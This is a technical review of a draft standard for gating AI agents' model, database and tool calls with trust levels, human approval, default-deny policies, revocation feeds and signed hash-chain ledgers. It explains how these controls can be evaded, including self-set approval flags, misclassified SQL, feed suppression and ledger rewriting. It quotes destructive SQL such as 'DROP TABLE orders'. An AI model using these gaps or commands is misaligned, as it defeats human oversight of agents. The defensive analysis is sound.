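| Calibration guide | 600 with a verified sponsor, 450 without one | At most 50 points a day | 2 points a day after a week of inactivity |
| Rust package | 500 | 10 points per success | 5 percent per hour |

With the Rust defaults, 20 quick successes would raise a new agent's score to 700, which the specification calls "trusted". Under the calibration guide, the same agent would have to wait at least seven days for promotion. Under the specification's defaults, an agent that starts at 500 and runs one report a week would fall to 164 between runs. The specification suggests revoking credentials below 300, so this agent would lose its access even though it was working as its owner intended.

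### What a good record can and cannot support

A record of successful actions is useful evidence about ordinary mistakes. If an agent completes 500 similar actions without a failure, the 95 percent upper bound on its failure rate is about 0.6 percent. That may be good enough for drafting replies, but an agent that makes 1,000 payments a day could still get six wrong each day. The calculation also assumes that future actions resemble past ones. Promotion lets the agent do something new, and 500 correct $10 payments are weak evidence of how it will handle a $50,000 one.

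An agent's record is an even weaker guide to how it will respond to prompt injection. An agent that has read 10,000 honest emails may still follow instructions in the first malicious one, and a high score increases the damage it can then do. Changes to the agent can also make its record irrelevant. In ATTP, an agent loses at most 20 points when its code no longer matches its specification, so one with a large surplus from past successes might not drop a level.

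Neither Sharif's ATTP draft nor Microsoft's calibration guide gives data on whether agents with higher scores cause fewer incidents. An operator would have better grounds for promoting an agent after testing it on the operations that the new level allows, including with injection attacks against its model, instructions and tools. The operator should repeat these tests whenever any of the three changes.

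A behavioural score is more useful for demotion than for promotion. Sudden changes in an agent's behaviour can be a sign of compromise, and a mistaken demotion usually does less harm than a mistaken promotion. The operator could set a fixed maximum level and use the score only to lower the agent's level from there. Microsoft's specification has a similar trust ceiling, which an agent cannot exceed however well it behaves. In *AGTP Trust and Verification Specification* (Hood, 2026), another individual Internet-Draft, a governance platform likewise assigns each agent a tier, and a separate score reflects the agent's behaviour.

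Attackers can try to exploit demotion. In Microsoft's specification, one agent's failure also lowers the scores of agents that have worked with it. An attacker who controls one agent could therefore make it fail repeatedly to restrict healthy agents that the business depends on.

### Approval at L4

Sharif's rules for L4 conflict. Under the general rule, an agent may perform any operation that requires its own level or lower, so an L4 agent could drop a table. But the definition of L4 requires the gate to refuse all L4 operations automatically and record the reason "human_approval_required". The draft's step-by-step procedure for model calls omits this refusal, so an L4 agent could call an L4 model immediately.

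If the gate does refuse, the agent's framework has to ask a person for approval through a separate channel, such as a phone app or a hardware token, and then send the call again. Sharif doesn't define any proof of approval that the agent could attach, so the second call is identical to the first. The gate therefore refuses the call again, and L4 operations can never run.

An implementer would have to add some signal, and a simple "approved" flag would be unsafe. The framework runs in the agent's container, where an agent that can write and run code could set the flag itself. The proof should instead come from an approval service outside the pod, which signs it after the person agrees. It could contain these fields:

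```json
{
  "agent": "spiffe://example.com/agent/infrastructure-bot",
  "target": "postgres://db:5432",
  "request_digest": "<SHA-256 of the exact statement>",
  "approver": "dana@example.com",
  "expires": "2026-10-07T14:35:00Z",
  "nonce": "7f3ac09e51d24b68"
}
```

The gate checks the signature with the approval service's public key, then compares the fields with the call. The approval includes the agent's identity, so another agent can't use it. The digest covers the exact statement, so the agent can't get approval for `DROP TABLE old_logs` and then send `DROP TABLE orders`. Sharif's gates already compute this digest for the ledger. The expiry time stops the agent from saving an approval for later. The nonce is a random value that the service never repeats, so the gate can reject an approval that has already been used.

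Single use is hard to enforce because Kubernetes often runs several copies of the same agent, each with its own gate. If each gate records only the nonces it has received, three copies could each use the same approval once. The gates need a shared record of used nonces, or the approval has to name a particular pod. Even a single-use approval can have an unexpected effect, because the hash fixes only the statement's text. A deletion of all orders marked "old" might match ten rows when the person approves it and 10,000 when it runs, so the expiry time should be short.

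Podala Narasimha avoids the retry by having the gateway hold the call while a person reviews the requester, the reason, the exact arguments and a preview of the changes. If the person approves, the gateway forwards the same call. The approval is tied to a hash of the tool and arguments, so the agent can't use it for a different action. It also expires, but the gateway must still mark it as used, or the agent could repeat the action before then.

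Sharif acknowledges in the ATTP draft that a valid signature shows only that the holder of a key produced it. A signature can't prove that anyone made a careful decision, because someone may have stolen the key or pressured its owner, or the owner may have clicked without reading.

### How carefully people review requests

Most of the recent evidence comes from Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, which can ask users for permission before it runs commands. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes "approval fatigue", in which people see so many requests that they stop reading them closely. Resilient Cyber's *The Human in the Loop Illusion* cites an early Anthropic figure that users approved 93 percent of requests. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) puts the share at 97 percent. Most of the commands were probably safe, so these rates don't prove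 that users were careless.

In an experiment by Anthropic, a research company hired 1,053 testers for a coding study and, partway through each session, replaced one permission request with a clearly dangerous command. Of the testers, 143 (13.6 percent) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17 percent early in a session and about 5 percent after 50 or more requests. Anthropic's automated classifier, which reviews commands in place of the user, blocked 89 percent of the same commands.

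The study has limits. Anthropic published it to support making the classifier the default in its product. The testers worked in a test environment where a destructive command could not harm anything of theirs, so they may have been less careful than an engineer in charge of a production database. The fall from 17 to 5 percent is more informative because the testers faced the same artificial conditions throughout. It suggests that frequent requests make people less careful.

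A second check may also add little. The testers caught only six dangerous commands that the classifier missed, so the two together would have stopped 943, compared with 937 for the classifier alone. Adding a second human reviewer helps more, but the pair could still miss most dangerous requests. mosiddi gives a sample rule that requires two approvals within 30 minutes for deletions and production writes. If each reviewer independently caught 13.6 percent of dangerous requests and either could block them, the pair would catch about 25 percent.

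People seem to pay more attention to larger decisions. Anthropic reports that users reject 39 percent of the plans Claude Code presents before starting work, compared with 3 percent of individual permission requests. Some of these rejections probably reflect disagreement about the approach rather than concern about safety, but they at least show that users read the plans. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

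Approval at L4 is therefore more likely to work if requests are rare and describe a whole change. Podala Narasimha reduces their number by varying the rule with the operation and the environment:

| Operation | Development | Staging | Production |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read | Automatic | Automatic | Automatic |
| Propose a change for review | Automatic | Automatic | Automatic |
| Make a change | Automatic | Automatic, with a notification | Approval |
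| Delete | Approval | Approval | Refused |

Where possible, the agent proposes a change to the cluster's configuration files, and an engineer reviews the whole proposal before it takes effect.

Sharif's database rules could produce far more approval requests. Dropping a table always requires L4, even if the agent created it as a temporary table a minute earlier, and a table rule can't lower that requirement. An agent that prepares data every hour and drops a temporary table each time would need 24 approvals a day, nearly all of them for harmless operations.

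## What happens when no rule matches or a component fails

Under default deny, a gate admits a call only if a rule explicitly permits it. Some policies also contain prohibitions, so the full rule is:

```
admit(call) = at least one rule permits the call
              and no rule forbids it
```

Under deny-by-default, an empty policy admits nothing. Sharif's draft follows this principle by requiring the sidecar to refuse any outbound call that no policy matches. The same section weakens the principle for models that the trust policy doesn't list. Instead of refusing the call outright, the gate uses the policy's `default_level` as the required level and compares it with the agent's level as usual.

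### Why the gate admits unlisted models

The gate uses `default_level` both as the level required to call an unlisted model and as the level of any agent without a more specific level setting. When such an agent calls an unlisted model, the two levels are equal, so the gate admits the call.

| *d* | Agent's level | Level an unlisted model requires | Result | SQL the agent may also run |
|---|---|---|---|---|
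| 0 | L0 | L0 | Admit | SELECT |
| 1 | L1 | L1 | Admit | SELECT, INSERT |
| 2 | L2 | L2 | Admit | The above, UPDATE, CREATE |
| 3 | L3 | L3 | Admit | The above, ALTER, DELETE |
| 4 | L4 | L4 | Unclear | The above; DROP and similar need approval |

The result for 4 is unclear because the draft's rules for L4 conflict. These results come from reading the draft's text, not from testing CyberSecAI's software, which may behave differently.

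The gate refuses an unlisted model to an agent whose assigned level is below *d*. In Sharif's sample policy file, *d* is 1 and the development namespace has a default of L0, so an agent with that default can't call unlisted models. An agent with the production default, L2, can call any of them. The file doesn't list `o3-pro`, which another of Sharif's examples rates at L3, so the model's requirement drops from L3 to L1.

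Sharif suggests that organisations check their policy files against their own requirements, for example that `default_level` in production must not be below 2. Setting it to 2 raises the trust level required to call unlisted models, but it also raises every agent that has no other assignment from L1 to L2, which lets those agents overwrite records. Setting it to 0 restricts unassigned agents to reading data, but lets every agent call every unlisted model.

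Two separate settings would solve this. Until the software has them, an operator can get much the same effect by giving the namespace its own default, which the gate checks before the global one:

```json
{
  "namespace_defaults": {"production": 0},
  "default_level": 4
}
```

An agent in production with no other assignment now gets L0. An unlisted model requires L4, and the same setting applies to unlisted stored procedures and unusual HTTP methods. If the operator misspells the namespace, every unassigned agent gets L4.

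### Starting without a trust policy

The policy file is optional. Without one, Sharif's gate defaults to level L1 and has no rules for particular models. It allows ordinary GET, POST, SELECT and INSERT calls, and calls to any model. It still refuses UPDATE and DELETE. If the software includes the optional personal-data check, the gate also refuses queries that name a personal-data column.

The missing file also contains the addresses of Vault and the revocation feed. Without them, the gate doesn't isolate credentials or poll the feed. The agent's database calls then succeed only if the agent has its own password, which the design is meant to prevent.

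This case could be common. Sharif's sample manifest puts the policy file in the `default` namespace, and a pod can only mount a ConfigMap from its own namespace. An operator who applies the samples as written and labels the production namespace for agents will have gates in production with no policy. The sample file also sets defaults for production, staging and development, but no pod in those namespaces can read the file, so the defaults have no effect.

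By contrast, Amazon's AgentCore, a service for running agents, denies everything when a policy engine has no policies, according to AWS's *Policy authoring guide*. An operator can get a similar result with the sidecar by changing `optional: true` to `optional: false`. Kubernetes then doesn't start the pod's containers until the file exists. This doesn't help if the file exists but contains invalid JSON, and the draft doesn't specify what the gate should do then.

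### Which calls could end in "no_policy_match"

Sharif lists "no_policy_match" ("default deny") among the reasons for a refusal. Very few calls can produce it, because most get either a fixed level from the built-in tables or the default level.

Three kinds of traffic remain:

- SQL statements that begin with some other keyword, such as WITH, COPY or BEGIN
- model requests in which the gate can't find a model name (Google's Gemini API, for example, puts the name in the web address, whereas Sharif's gate looks for it in the request body)
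- protocols that none of the three gates can parse, such as Redis or SMTP

The draft doesn't give these calls a level, so the general rule should apply and they should end in "no_policy_match", though the draft doesn't state this. Refusing every unknown SQL keyword would block reports that start with WITH. It would also block agents that use Psycopg, a common PostgreSQL driver for Python, with its default settings, because it sends BEGIN before their first statement.

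The draft's built-in tables can consistently be read as a policy, in which case a GET request does match a rule. Under that reading, the policy permits every agent to read from any web address, and default deny blocks very little.

### Policies that permit only what they list

Cedar is an open-source policy language in which each policy either permits or forbids something. Its engine checks each request against all the policies and denies it if any "forbid" policy applies. Otherwise, the engine allows the request if any "permit" policy applies and denies it if none does. It never falls back on a default level, so an empty set of policies denies every request.

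Strands Agents' *Cedar Authorization* describes how a toolkit for building agents uses this language to check tool calls. Its basic example is a single policy:

```
permit(principal, action == Action::"search", resource);
```

The agent has two tools, and the user asks it to search for quarterly reports and then delete record 42.

| Tool | Policy that applies | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `search` | The "permit" policy | Allow |
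| `delete_record` | None | Deny |

Nobody had to anticipate `delete_record` or rate its danger. By contrast, Sharif's gate would require only L1 for the same tool on an MCP server without a route rule. But the toolkit checks calls inside the agent's own process, so it has the same weakness as Aegis against agents that run their own code. Tigera's Lynx evaluates the same kind of policy outside the agent, in a shared gateway, according to Help Net Security.

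Misspellings are also less dangerous. If an operator enters `o3-por` in Sharif's policy file, the entry matches nothing and the real model gets the default level. In Cedar, a misspelled tool name in a "permit" policy blocks a tool that should work, and someone will notice. Strands Agents can compare the policies with the agent's list of tools and reject any name that isn't on it.

A prohibition can still let calls through when they spell the forbidden value differently or leave it out. Strands Agents gives the example of a deployment tool that should work only in test environments. A rule that forbids "production" would miss "Production", "prod" and a call with no environment. A rule that permits only "staging" and "dev" refuses all three.

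Prohibitions are more useful as an emergency stop. In an example from AWS, one policy permits a refund agent to pay refunds under $500, and a second forbids all refunds. An operator can add the second policy to block even a $200 refund, without having to find and remove every policy that permits refunds. Sharif's revocation feed can stop an agent or a model, but it can't stop an individual tool.

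If a policy causes an error, the Cedar engine skips it and decides using the others. This can happen when a policy refers to the amount of a refund and the request doesn't include one. Cedar's designers considered denying the request instead, but an application with 100 working policies could then start refusing everything because of an error in the 101st. Skipping a faulty "permit" policy is safe because the agent only loses a permission, but skipping a "forbid" policy may allow a call that the operator meant to block. Applications can inspect the errors and override the decision, and Strands Agents denies any call for which the evaluation fails. Denying the call is the better choice for an agent that handles money, even though one bad policy could stop its work.

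In Open Policy Agent, the operator has to write the default. The rules define when `allow` is true, and if none applies, the result is undefined rather than false. Open Policy Agent's *Rego Keyword Examples* shows how the line `default allow := false` makes the result false instead. In the example, a rule looks for a field called `admin`, but the request contains a list of roles that includes "admin". The rule doesn't match, so `allow` defaults to false and the request is refused.

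Without that line, the software that asks for the decision has to handle the missing answer. Older Open Policy Agent documentation describes the reply as a success response (status 200) with no `result` field. A gate that blocks calls only when `result` is false would let the call through. The gate should admit a call only when `result` is present and true.

A proposal from the Kubernetes project would bring default deny for MCP tools into the cluster's own configuration. Under Kubernetes' *Tool Authorization in Agentic Networking*, an agent may connect to an MCP server and list its tools, but it can't call any of them unless a policy names both the agent's service account and the tool. The worked example has two agents and two servers:

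| Tool | First agent | Second agent |
|---|---|---|
| `add` | Allow | Deny |
| `subtract` | Allow | Allow |
| `read_wiki_structure` | Deny | Allow |
| `ask_question` | Deny | Deny |

As with the payroll and clinic agents, no ordered set of levels could produce this table.

The proposal is not ready for use. A prototype exists, but Kubernetes warns against running it in production, and Kubernetes' *API design* describes the interface as early alpha. The proposal also leaves out how the gateway verifies an agent's identity, and agents can still see tools they aren't allowed to call.

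### What the draft specifies for each failure

When a gate can't make or carry out a decision, Sharif requires it to fail closed in some cases, allows it to fail open in others, and leaves the remaining cases to the implementer.

| Failure | Response in the draft | Classification |
|---|---|---|
| The gate crashes | None, apart from a health check that triggers a restart | Unspecified |
| The trust policy is missing | The agent gets L1, and so does every model | Fail open up to L1 |
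| The secret store is unreachable | None | Unspecified |
| The ledger's disk is full | The gate fails closed if it can't write a record | Fail closed |
| The revocation feed is unreachable | No change for five minutes, then the gate refuses L3 and L4 operations | Fail open up to L2, fail closed above it |

If the gate crashes, the agent's calls usually stop. When packet redirection sends them to the gate's port, the connections fail because nothing is listening there. If only proxy variables route the calls, the result depends on the client, because some programs may try a direct connection when the proxy doesn't respond. If the gate hangs instead, the agent could wait about 30 seconds for a restart, because Sharif has Kubernetes check the gate every 10 seconds and Kubernetes by default restarts it after three failed checks.

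Database access also fails closed in practice when the secret store is down, because the gate can't create an account and the agent has no password of its own. The gate may reuse an earlier account until it expires, so a few statements might still run in the first minute. After that, all database work stops for every agent that depends on that store. Anyone who took over the gate could steal a permanent password kept there as a fallback.

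The requirement to fail closed when the disk is full appears only in an appendix table that compares the design with an industrial security standard. The main text specifies how to export a full ledger but not what to do when a write fails. Sharif requires the gate to save the record of a model call before it returns the response, but the model may already have processed the request by then. The draft has no such requirement for databases. If the gate ran a DELETE first and then failed to write the record, the agent would get an error even though the row was gone. The gate should therefore save the record before it forwards the call. Kubernetes may evict a pod whose ledger exceeds the volume's size limit, which also stops the agent.

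The draft doesn't cover certificates that expire because the gate can't reach the certificate authority. Suppose an agent's certificate gives it L1 and its namespace default is L2. If the gate ignored the expired certificate and fell back to the namespace default, an outage could raise the agent to L2. The gate should refuse all of the agent's calls until the agent has a valid certificate again.

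### How a revocation reaches the gates

If an agent starts to misbehave, the operator needs to stop it at every gate. In Sharif's design, a trust authority (the party allowed to issue revocations) publishes a signed entry like this one:

```json
{
  "seq": 43,
  "revocation": {
    "subject": "agent",
    "id": "production/support-agent",
    "reason": "prompt_injection",
    "timestamp": "2026-10-07T09:15:00Z"
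  },
  "feed_signature": "<signature>"
}
```

Each gate polls the feed every 30 seconds by default and requests entries newer than the last one it processed. It checks each signature and applies the entries in order. After applying an entry that names an agent, the gate refuses everything that agent tries to do, whatever its trust level. An entry can also name a model, in which case the gates refuse calls to that model from all agents.

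An agent that makes 10 calls a second can make up to 300 calls, or 150 on average, between the publication of the entry and the next poll. If the agent runs in three pods, each with its own gate and the same call rate, the maximum is 900. These figures exclude calls made while someone notices the problem and publishes the entry. Sharif also allows feeds that push entries to the gates. With a half-second delay, the agent would make about five more calls.

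The situation is worse if the gate can't reach the feed. For the first five minutes nothing changes, so the same agent could make another 3,000 calls. The gate then refuses operations that require L3 or L4 but keeps evaluating the rest normally. If the gate never received an agent's revocation, that agent keeps its access to L0 to L2 operations until the outage ends. A customer service agent at L1 therefore keeps all its access, and an agent at L2 can still change every order by running `UPDATE orders SET status = 'cancelled'`.

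Sharif lets operators change the timeout and the highest trust level that the gate permits during an outage, and writes that organisations may choose to refuse everything. But the lowest level, 0, still permits reading, and the policy schema doesn't describe a value that refuses all calls.

Failing closed also disrupts healthy agents. If the feed is down for more than five minutes, they lose their L3 and L4 operations in every connected cluster. An attacker who wanted to stop a company's trading agents could try to take the feed offline. A second feed makes this harder, because the gate enters restricted mode only when it can't reach any of its feeds. But if the two feeds carried different entries, an attacker could block just the one with the relevant revocation without triggering restricted mode.

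Sequence numbers are supposed to stop an attacker from replaying an old copy of the feed. Each response includes the latest number in a field called `head`, and the gate rejects the response if this is lower than the last number it processed. The signatures cover the individual entries but not `head`, so an attacker who controls the feed server could keep returning the current number with no new entries. The gate would accept each response as up to date, never enter the restricted mode and never receive the revocation. The attacker could also leave out a single entry, because Sharif requires the numbers to rise but not to be consecutive. To prevent both attacks, the authority could sign each response with a short expiry time, and the gate could reject any gap in the numbers.

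Sharif specifies how a restarted gate restores its ledger, but not how it restores its list of revocations or the last sequence number it read from the feed. Until its first successful poll, the gate may admit calls from an agent that it refused before the restart. It also has no earlier number to compare, so it cannot recognise an old copy of the feed. An implementer could rebuild the list from the ledger, which records each revocation, or have the gate refuse all calls until it has read the feed.

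A revocation can also fail because the agent's names don match. Sharif's sample entry identifies the agent as `production/trading-bot-1`, but a SPIFFE certificate would identify it as something like `spiffe://example.com/agentmesh/production/trading-bot-1`. If the gate compares the two literally, it won't block the agent. Operators should test this by revoking a harmless agent before they need the feed in an emergency.

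A revocation list works like a list of prohibitions, so a gate that receives no updates keeps admitting calls. A stricter design would require each gate to hold a signed statement, valid for perhaps a minute, that the agent may continue. The authority would stop an agent by not renewing the statement. A lost connection would then stop the agent too, which is safer but makes all the agents' work depend on the authority being available. An operator could require such statements only for agents that can change or delete data.

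### From logging to enforcement

Switching on default deny in a running system blocks every request the policy doesn't cover. In its review of existing tools, Kubernetes warns of this problem in Istio, where an "allow" policy that mistakenly covers a whole namespace can block all traffic there. Sharif's installation steps carry a similar risk. If an agent has been updating records and its pod restarts with a gate but no policy, the agent is at L1 and its updates fail.

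Operators can reduce the risk by starting with a mode that only logs. AWS's *GatewayPolicyEngineConfiguration* describes two settings for Amazon's agent gateway: `LOG_ONLY`, in which the policy engine records whether it would have allowed each call but doesn't block any, and `ENFORCE`, in which it blocks the calls that the policies deny. AWS recommends testing policies in `LOG_ONLY` to avoid disrupting production traffic. Sharif's draft has no equivalent, so an implementer would have to add one.

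The logging period should be long enough to include rare work, such as an agent's month-end reports. Someone then has to review each call that the gate would have refused and decide whether to add a permission. Generating permissions automatically from the whole log would be quicker, but if an attacker had injected instructions during that period, the new policy would also permit the attacker's calls.

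A log also can't show how an agent will react to a refusal. Once the gate blocks one tool, the agent may give up, repeat the call many times or try another tool to get the same result. The operator can learn this only by enforcing the policy, preferably in a test environment first and then for a few agents whose failures would do little harm. A rollout can also be limited by installation. According to *Deny-by-default ACL configuration* from ServiceNow, which sells workflow software, the company's stricter default for AI agents applies to freshly reset installations. This avoids breaking existing agents, but older installations may stay more permissive until someone changes them.

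Wrongful refusals are a bigger problem for agents than for single requests, because one task can involve many calls. If the gate wrongly refused 1 percent of calls at random, a task with 20 calls would have an 18 percent chance of at least one refusal (1 − 0.99^20). A refusal partway through a task can also leave work half done. For example, an agent might cancel a customer's old order and then be unable to create the new one.

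Errors under default deny are usually systematic. If the operator forgets to write a rule for a tool, every call to it fails, so the problem is easy to find and one new rule fixes it. False alarms from pattern matching are harder to fix because they depend on the text of each call.

When the gate refuses a call that an agent needs, the quickest fix with a list of permitted tools is to add that one tool for that agent. The quickest fix with Sharif's levels is often to raise the agent's level, which grants it all the extra rights of the higher level. The operator should limit who can switch the gate back to logging only, where it blocks nothing, because a team with a broken agent and a deadline will want to make that switch.

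## What the ledger records and what it can prove

The gate writes each decision to a file named `evidence.jsonl` as one line of JSON. If the customer service agent at L1 tried to delete an order, the record would look like this, with the long values shortened:

```json
{
  "n": 1,
  "kind": "refuse",
  "gate_type": "db",
  "signer_id": "sidecar-7f3a",
  "agent_id": "production/support-agent",
  "target": "postgres://db:5432 DELETE FROM orders",
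  "trust_level": 1,
  "required_level": 3,
  "decision": "refuse",
  "reason": "insufficient_trust_level",
  "request_digest": "5be1...",
  "timestamp": "2026-10-07T09:15:00.000Z",
  "prev": "a1f3...",
  "h": "7c20...",
  "signature": "MEUC..."
}
```

Six of the fields contain the agent's identity, the two trust levels, the decision, the reason and the time. The other nine need some explanation:

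| Field | Contents |
|---|---|
| `n` | The record's position in the ledger, starting at 0 |
| `kind` | "admit", "refuse", "revoke", "startup" or "shutdown" |
| `gate_type` | The gate that decided, or "system" for events such as a startup |
| `signer_id` | An identifier for the gate's signing key |
| `target` | The model's name, the database's address and the start of the statement, or the HTTP method and URL |
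| `request_digest` | A hash of the full SQL statement or request body |
| `prev` | The previous record's hash |
| `h` | This record's own hash |
| `signature` | The gate's signature over `h` |

A hash is a fixed-length value computed from data. Sharif uses SHA-256, and nobody knows a practical way to find two inputs with the same SHA-256 hash, so a changed record will not match its old hash.

These records lack several facts that an investigator would need. After a model call, the gate should write a second record with a hash of the model's response, but the two records share no call number, so if an agent has several requests open at once, the ledger doesn't show which response belongs to which request. Sharif also claims that one signature covers both hashes, which can't be true if they are in separate records.

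For database calls, the ledger omits the name of the temporary account that the gate used, so an investigator has to match the ledger with the database's own log by time, which is unreliable for a busy agent. The ledger also has no field for who approved an L4 operation or which version of the trust policy was in force.

The `target` field, by contrast, can contain too much. If an agent puts a customer list in a web address, the gate copies the whole address into the ledger. This helps the investigation, but it also exposes the customer list to anyone who can read the ledger.

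### What one record proves

A valid record proves that someone with the gate's key signed a statement that the gate made this decision, but not that the decision was right. If the gate mistakes `EXPLAIN ANALYZE DELETE FROM orders` for a read, the ledger will contain a correctly signed record of a permitted L0 operation, even though the command deleted every row in `orders`.

The ledger also can't prove that the agent made no other calls, because a call that bypasses the gate leaves no record. Outside logs can help, since Vault can log each database account it creates and the database can log each login. A login with no matching ledger record suggests that a call bypassed the gate or that someone removed a record.

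The time in each record comes from the gate's own clock, so it is only as reliable as that clock. The `request_digest` is useful mainly to someone who already has a copy of the request, because a hash can't be directly converted back to text. However, anyone with the ledger can recover a short statement by guessing. They can hash `DELETE FROM orders WHERE id = 1`, then the same statement with 2, and so on until a hash matches. This lets investigators recover a missing order number, but also lets an intruder recover a customer's identity number from a query.

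### Checking a chain of three records

The records form a chain because each one contains the hash of the one before:

```
prev(0) = 64 zeros
prev(i) = h(i-1)
h(i)    = SHA-256(JCS(fields n to prev of record i))
sig(i)  = Sign(private key, h(i))
```

The JSON Canonicalization Scheme (JCS) is a standard way of writing JSON so that the same data always produces the same bytes. The signature algorithm is ECDSA with the P-256 curve. Because `h(i)` covers `prev(i)`, each hash depends on every earlier record. Yuan and colleagues describe Aegis as keeping a similar chain, with a separate signing key for each agent.

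A verifier needs the ledger and the gate's public key. Suppose an agent at L3 starts up, deletes some orders and then reads a public table. The hashes here are short stand-ins:

| `n` | Event | `prev` | `h` |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | Startup | 0000 | a1f3 |
| 1 | `DELETE FROM orders` | a1f3 | 7c20 |
| 2 | `SELECT title FROM public_content` | 7c20 | e95b |

For each record, the verifier makes three checks:

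1. The link check compares `prev` with the hash that the verifier calculated for the previous record, or with zeros for record 0.
2. The hash check recalculates the record's hash from its fields and compares the result with `h`.
3. The signature check tests the signature against `h` and the public key.

All three records pass. Suppose someone tries to hide the deletion by changing the target in record 1 to a SELECT. The verifier calculates a new hash for that record, say 4d88, which doesn't match the stored 7c20, so the hash check fails. Record 2 still has 7c20 in its `prev` field, so its link check fails too. The signature check on record 1 passes because the old signature still matches the old `h`.

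A more careful attacker would recalculate the hashes too:

| What the attacker changes | Record 1 | Record 2 |
|---|---|---|
| The target in record 1 | Hash check fails | Link check fails |
| The target and `h` in record 1 | Signature check fails | Link check fails |
| The above, and `prev` and `h` in record 2 | Signature check fails | Signature check fails |
| The above, and both signatures, made with the gate's key | Passes | Passes |

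Without the key, the attacker can't make the altered record pass verification. The chain also reveals an insertion or deletion in the middle. If the attacker removes record 1, record 2's `prev` no longer matches the hash of the record before it.

### Missing tails and rewritten ledgers

If the attacker removes record 2 instead, records 0 and 1 still pass every check. A hash chain can't reveal that its end is missing, because no remaining record refers to the missing ones. Sharif proposes comparing the ledger's length with the expected length but doesn't say how an auditor would learn that length. The gate can write a "shutdown" record when it stops, so a ledger without one may mean that someone removed the end, but a crash also leaves the ledger without one.

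A restart makes the loss harder to detect. Suppose the ledger has 1,000 records and someone deletes the last 100. The running gate has the latest hash in memory, so its next record won't link to the shortened file. But if the gate restarts first, it takes the last hash from the 900 remaining records and continues from there. The chain is then valid, and the attacker doesn't need the key. The agent normally can't do this because only the sidecar mounts the volume, but a node administrator can, and so can anyone with permission to run commands in the sidecar.

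Damaged files cause a related problem. If the gate crashes while writing record 500, the file ends in half a line. Sharif requires the gate to restore the records before the damage and resume from the last valid one, but also forbids it to shorten or overwrite the file. The fragment therefore stays, and the gate writes a new record 500 after it. At the next restart, the gate stops reading at the same fragment, resumes from record 499 and writes a second record 500. The records written between the two restarts are not part of the chain that the gate is now extending. An implementer could avoid this by moving the damaged file aside and starting a new one whose first record notes the damage.

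Whoever holds the signing key can rewrite the whole ledger, as the last row of the table shows. In Sharif's design, the gate holds this key, so an attacker who takes over the gate can rewrite the ledger. The operator can too, which matters when the operator is under investigation, for example after its agent has lost a customer's money.

By default, the gate creates a new key pair each time it starts and publishes the public key at its health-check address. Sharif's verification procedure uses a single public key, so if a ledger spans a restart, the signatures made either before or after the restart fail verification. The auditor needs every public key the gate has used, and someone has to save each one while the gate is running. Otherwise, an attacker could rewrite the old records, sign them with a fresh key and claim the key was the gate's.

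Sharif recommends supplying the key from Vault or a key management service in production. A permanent key makes verification simpler, but an attacker who copies it can re-sign the ledger back to its first record. With a new key at each start, an attacker who copies the current one can't re-sign records from before the last restart, provided an independent party has the old public keys. A service that signs without releasing the key is a middle option. The attacker can request false signatures only while controlling the gate, but could use that time to re-sign old records as well.

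### Sending the latest hash to an independent party

The usual remedy for both problems, called anchoring, is to send the latest hash at regular intervals to an independent party who can't be tempted or forced to change it. The latest hash depends on all earlier records, so that one hash is enough to check the entire ledger up to that point. If the independent party has the hash of record 6,000, a ledger that ends at record 5,900 is visibly too short, and a ledger that someone has rewritten and re-signed has a different hash for record 6,000.

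Records written since the last message remain exposed. If the gate writes *r* records a second and sends a hash every *T* seconds, up to *rT* recent records can vanish unnoticed. At 10 records a second:

| Interval | Records that can vanish | Messages per agent per day |
|---|---|---|
| 1 second | 10 | 86,400 |
| 60 seconds | 600 | 1,440 |
| 1 hour | 36,000 | 24 |

The recipient should also raise an alarm when an expected message doesn't arrive, because an attacker could block the messages and enlarge the gap. To detect the loss of an entire ledger, the recipient needs a list of the agent pods that have started. The cluster's audit log can supply this list if the attacker can't change the log.

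Sharif recommends anchoring but doesn't require it, and suggests a trusted timestamping service. Such a service signs the hash together with the time, which proves the ledger existed by then. But the service may not keep a copy of what it signed. If the operator stores the signed timestamps beside the ledger, an attacker can delete both, so another party should hold the timestamps.

Sharif also suggests exporting the records themselves to storage that prevents changes for a fixed period. If the gate sends each record as soon as it writes it, only records still in transit are exposed to tampering, and the operator keeps the records' contents as well as proof that they existed. At 20 records a second and 700 bytes a record, each agent needs only 14 kilobytes a second of bandwidth. The choice of storage account matters more than the bandwidth, because an administrator who can delete the account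 can delete the records in it.

Anchoring can't ensure that the gate writes true records. An attacker who controls the gate can write false records and send their hashes on schedule. The independent party can then prove only that nobody changed those records afterwards.

### Merkle trees and short proofs

Checking a single record in a hash chain is slow because the auditor needs every record between it and the latest hash. *Efficient Data Structures for Tamper-Evident Logging* (Crosby and Wallach, 2009) compares a hash chain with the paper's own design on a log of 80 million events. To prove that a randomly chosen event was in the log, a hash chain would need an average of 40 million hashes, while the paper's design needed about 3,100 bytes.

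They use a Merkle tree, which combines hashes in pairs until only one is left. With four records, a to d, and a hash function H:

```
ab   = H(H(a), H(b))
cd   = H(H(c), H(d))
root = H(ab, cd)
```

The root depends on all four records, like the latest hash in a chain. (Real systems also mark single records and pairs differently, so that nobody can pass off one as the other.)

An inclusion proof shows that a record is in the log. To prove that c is in this log, the operator supplies c, H(d) and `ab`. The auditor calculates H(c), combines it with H(d) to get `cd`, combines that with `ab` and compares the result with the root. The number of hashes in the proof grows with the logarithm of the number of records. For 150,000 records, 18 hashes are enough, or 576 bytes with SHA-256. An operator could therefore show a customer the record about a disputed refund without revealing any others.

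A consistency proof shows that a newer log still contains everything in an older one. Suppose the auditor saved the root `ab` when the log had only a and b. The operator supplies `cd`, and the auditor checks that H(`ab`, `cd`) equals the new root. If the operator had changed b since then, nobody could find a value of `cd` that makes the hash match the new root.

These proofs help only if someone asks for them. Crosby and Wallach treat the log's operator as untrusted and point out that an operator can tamper with the records under a root if they know nobody will check it. An operator can also keep two versions of the log and show them to different auditors. Each auditor would receive valid proofs, so the auditors have to compare roots to detect this.

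For a single gate with a 100 MiB ledger, a Merkle tree adds little, since an auditor can read the whole file in seconds. It is more useful for a central log that collects records from many gates. A hundred agents that each write 20 records a second would produce 2,000 a second. Crosby and Wallach's prototype handled 1,750 a second on one processor core, or 10,500 when other hardware made the signatures, and current hardware should be faster.

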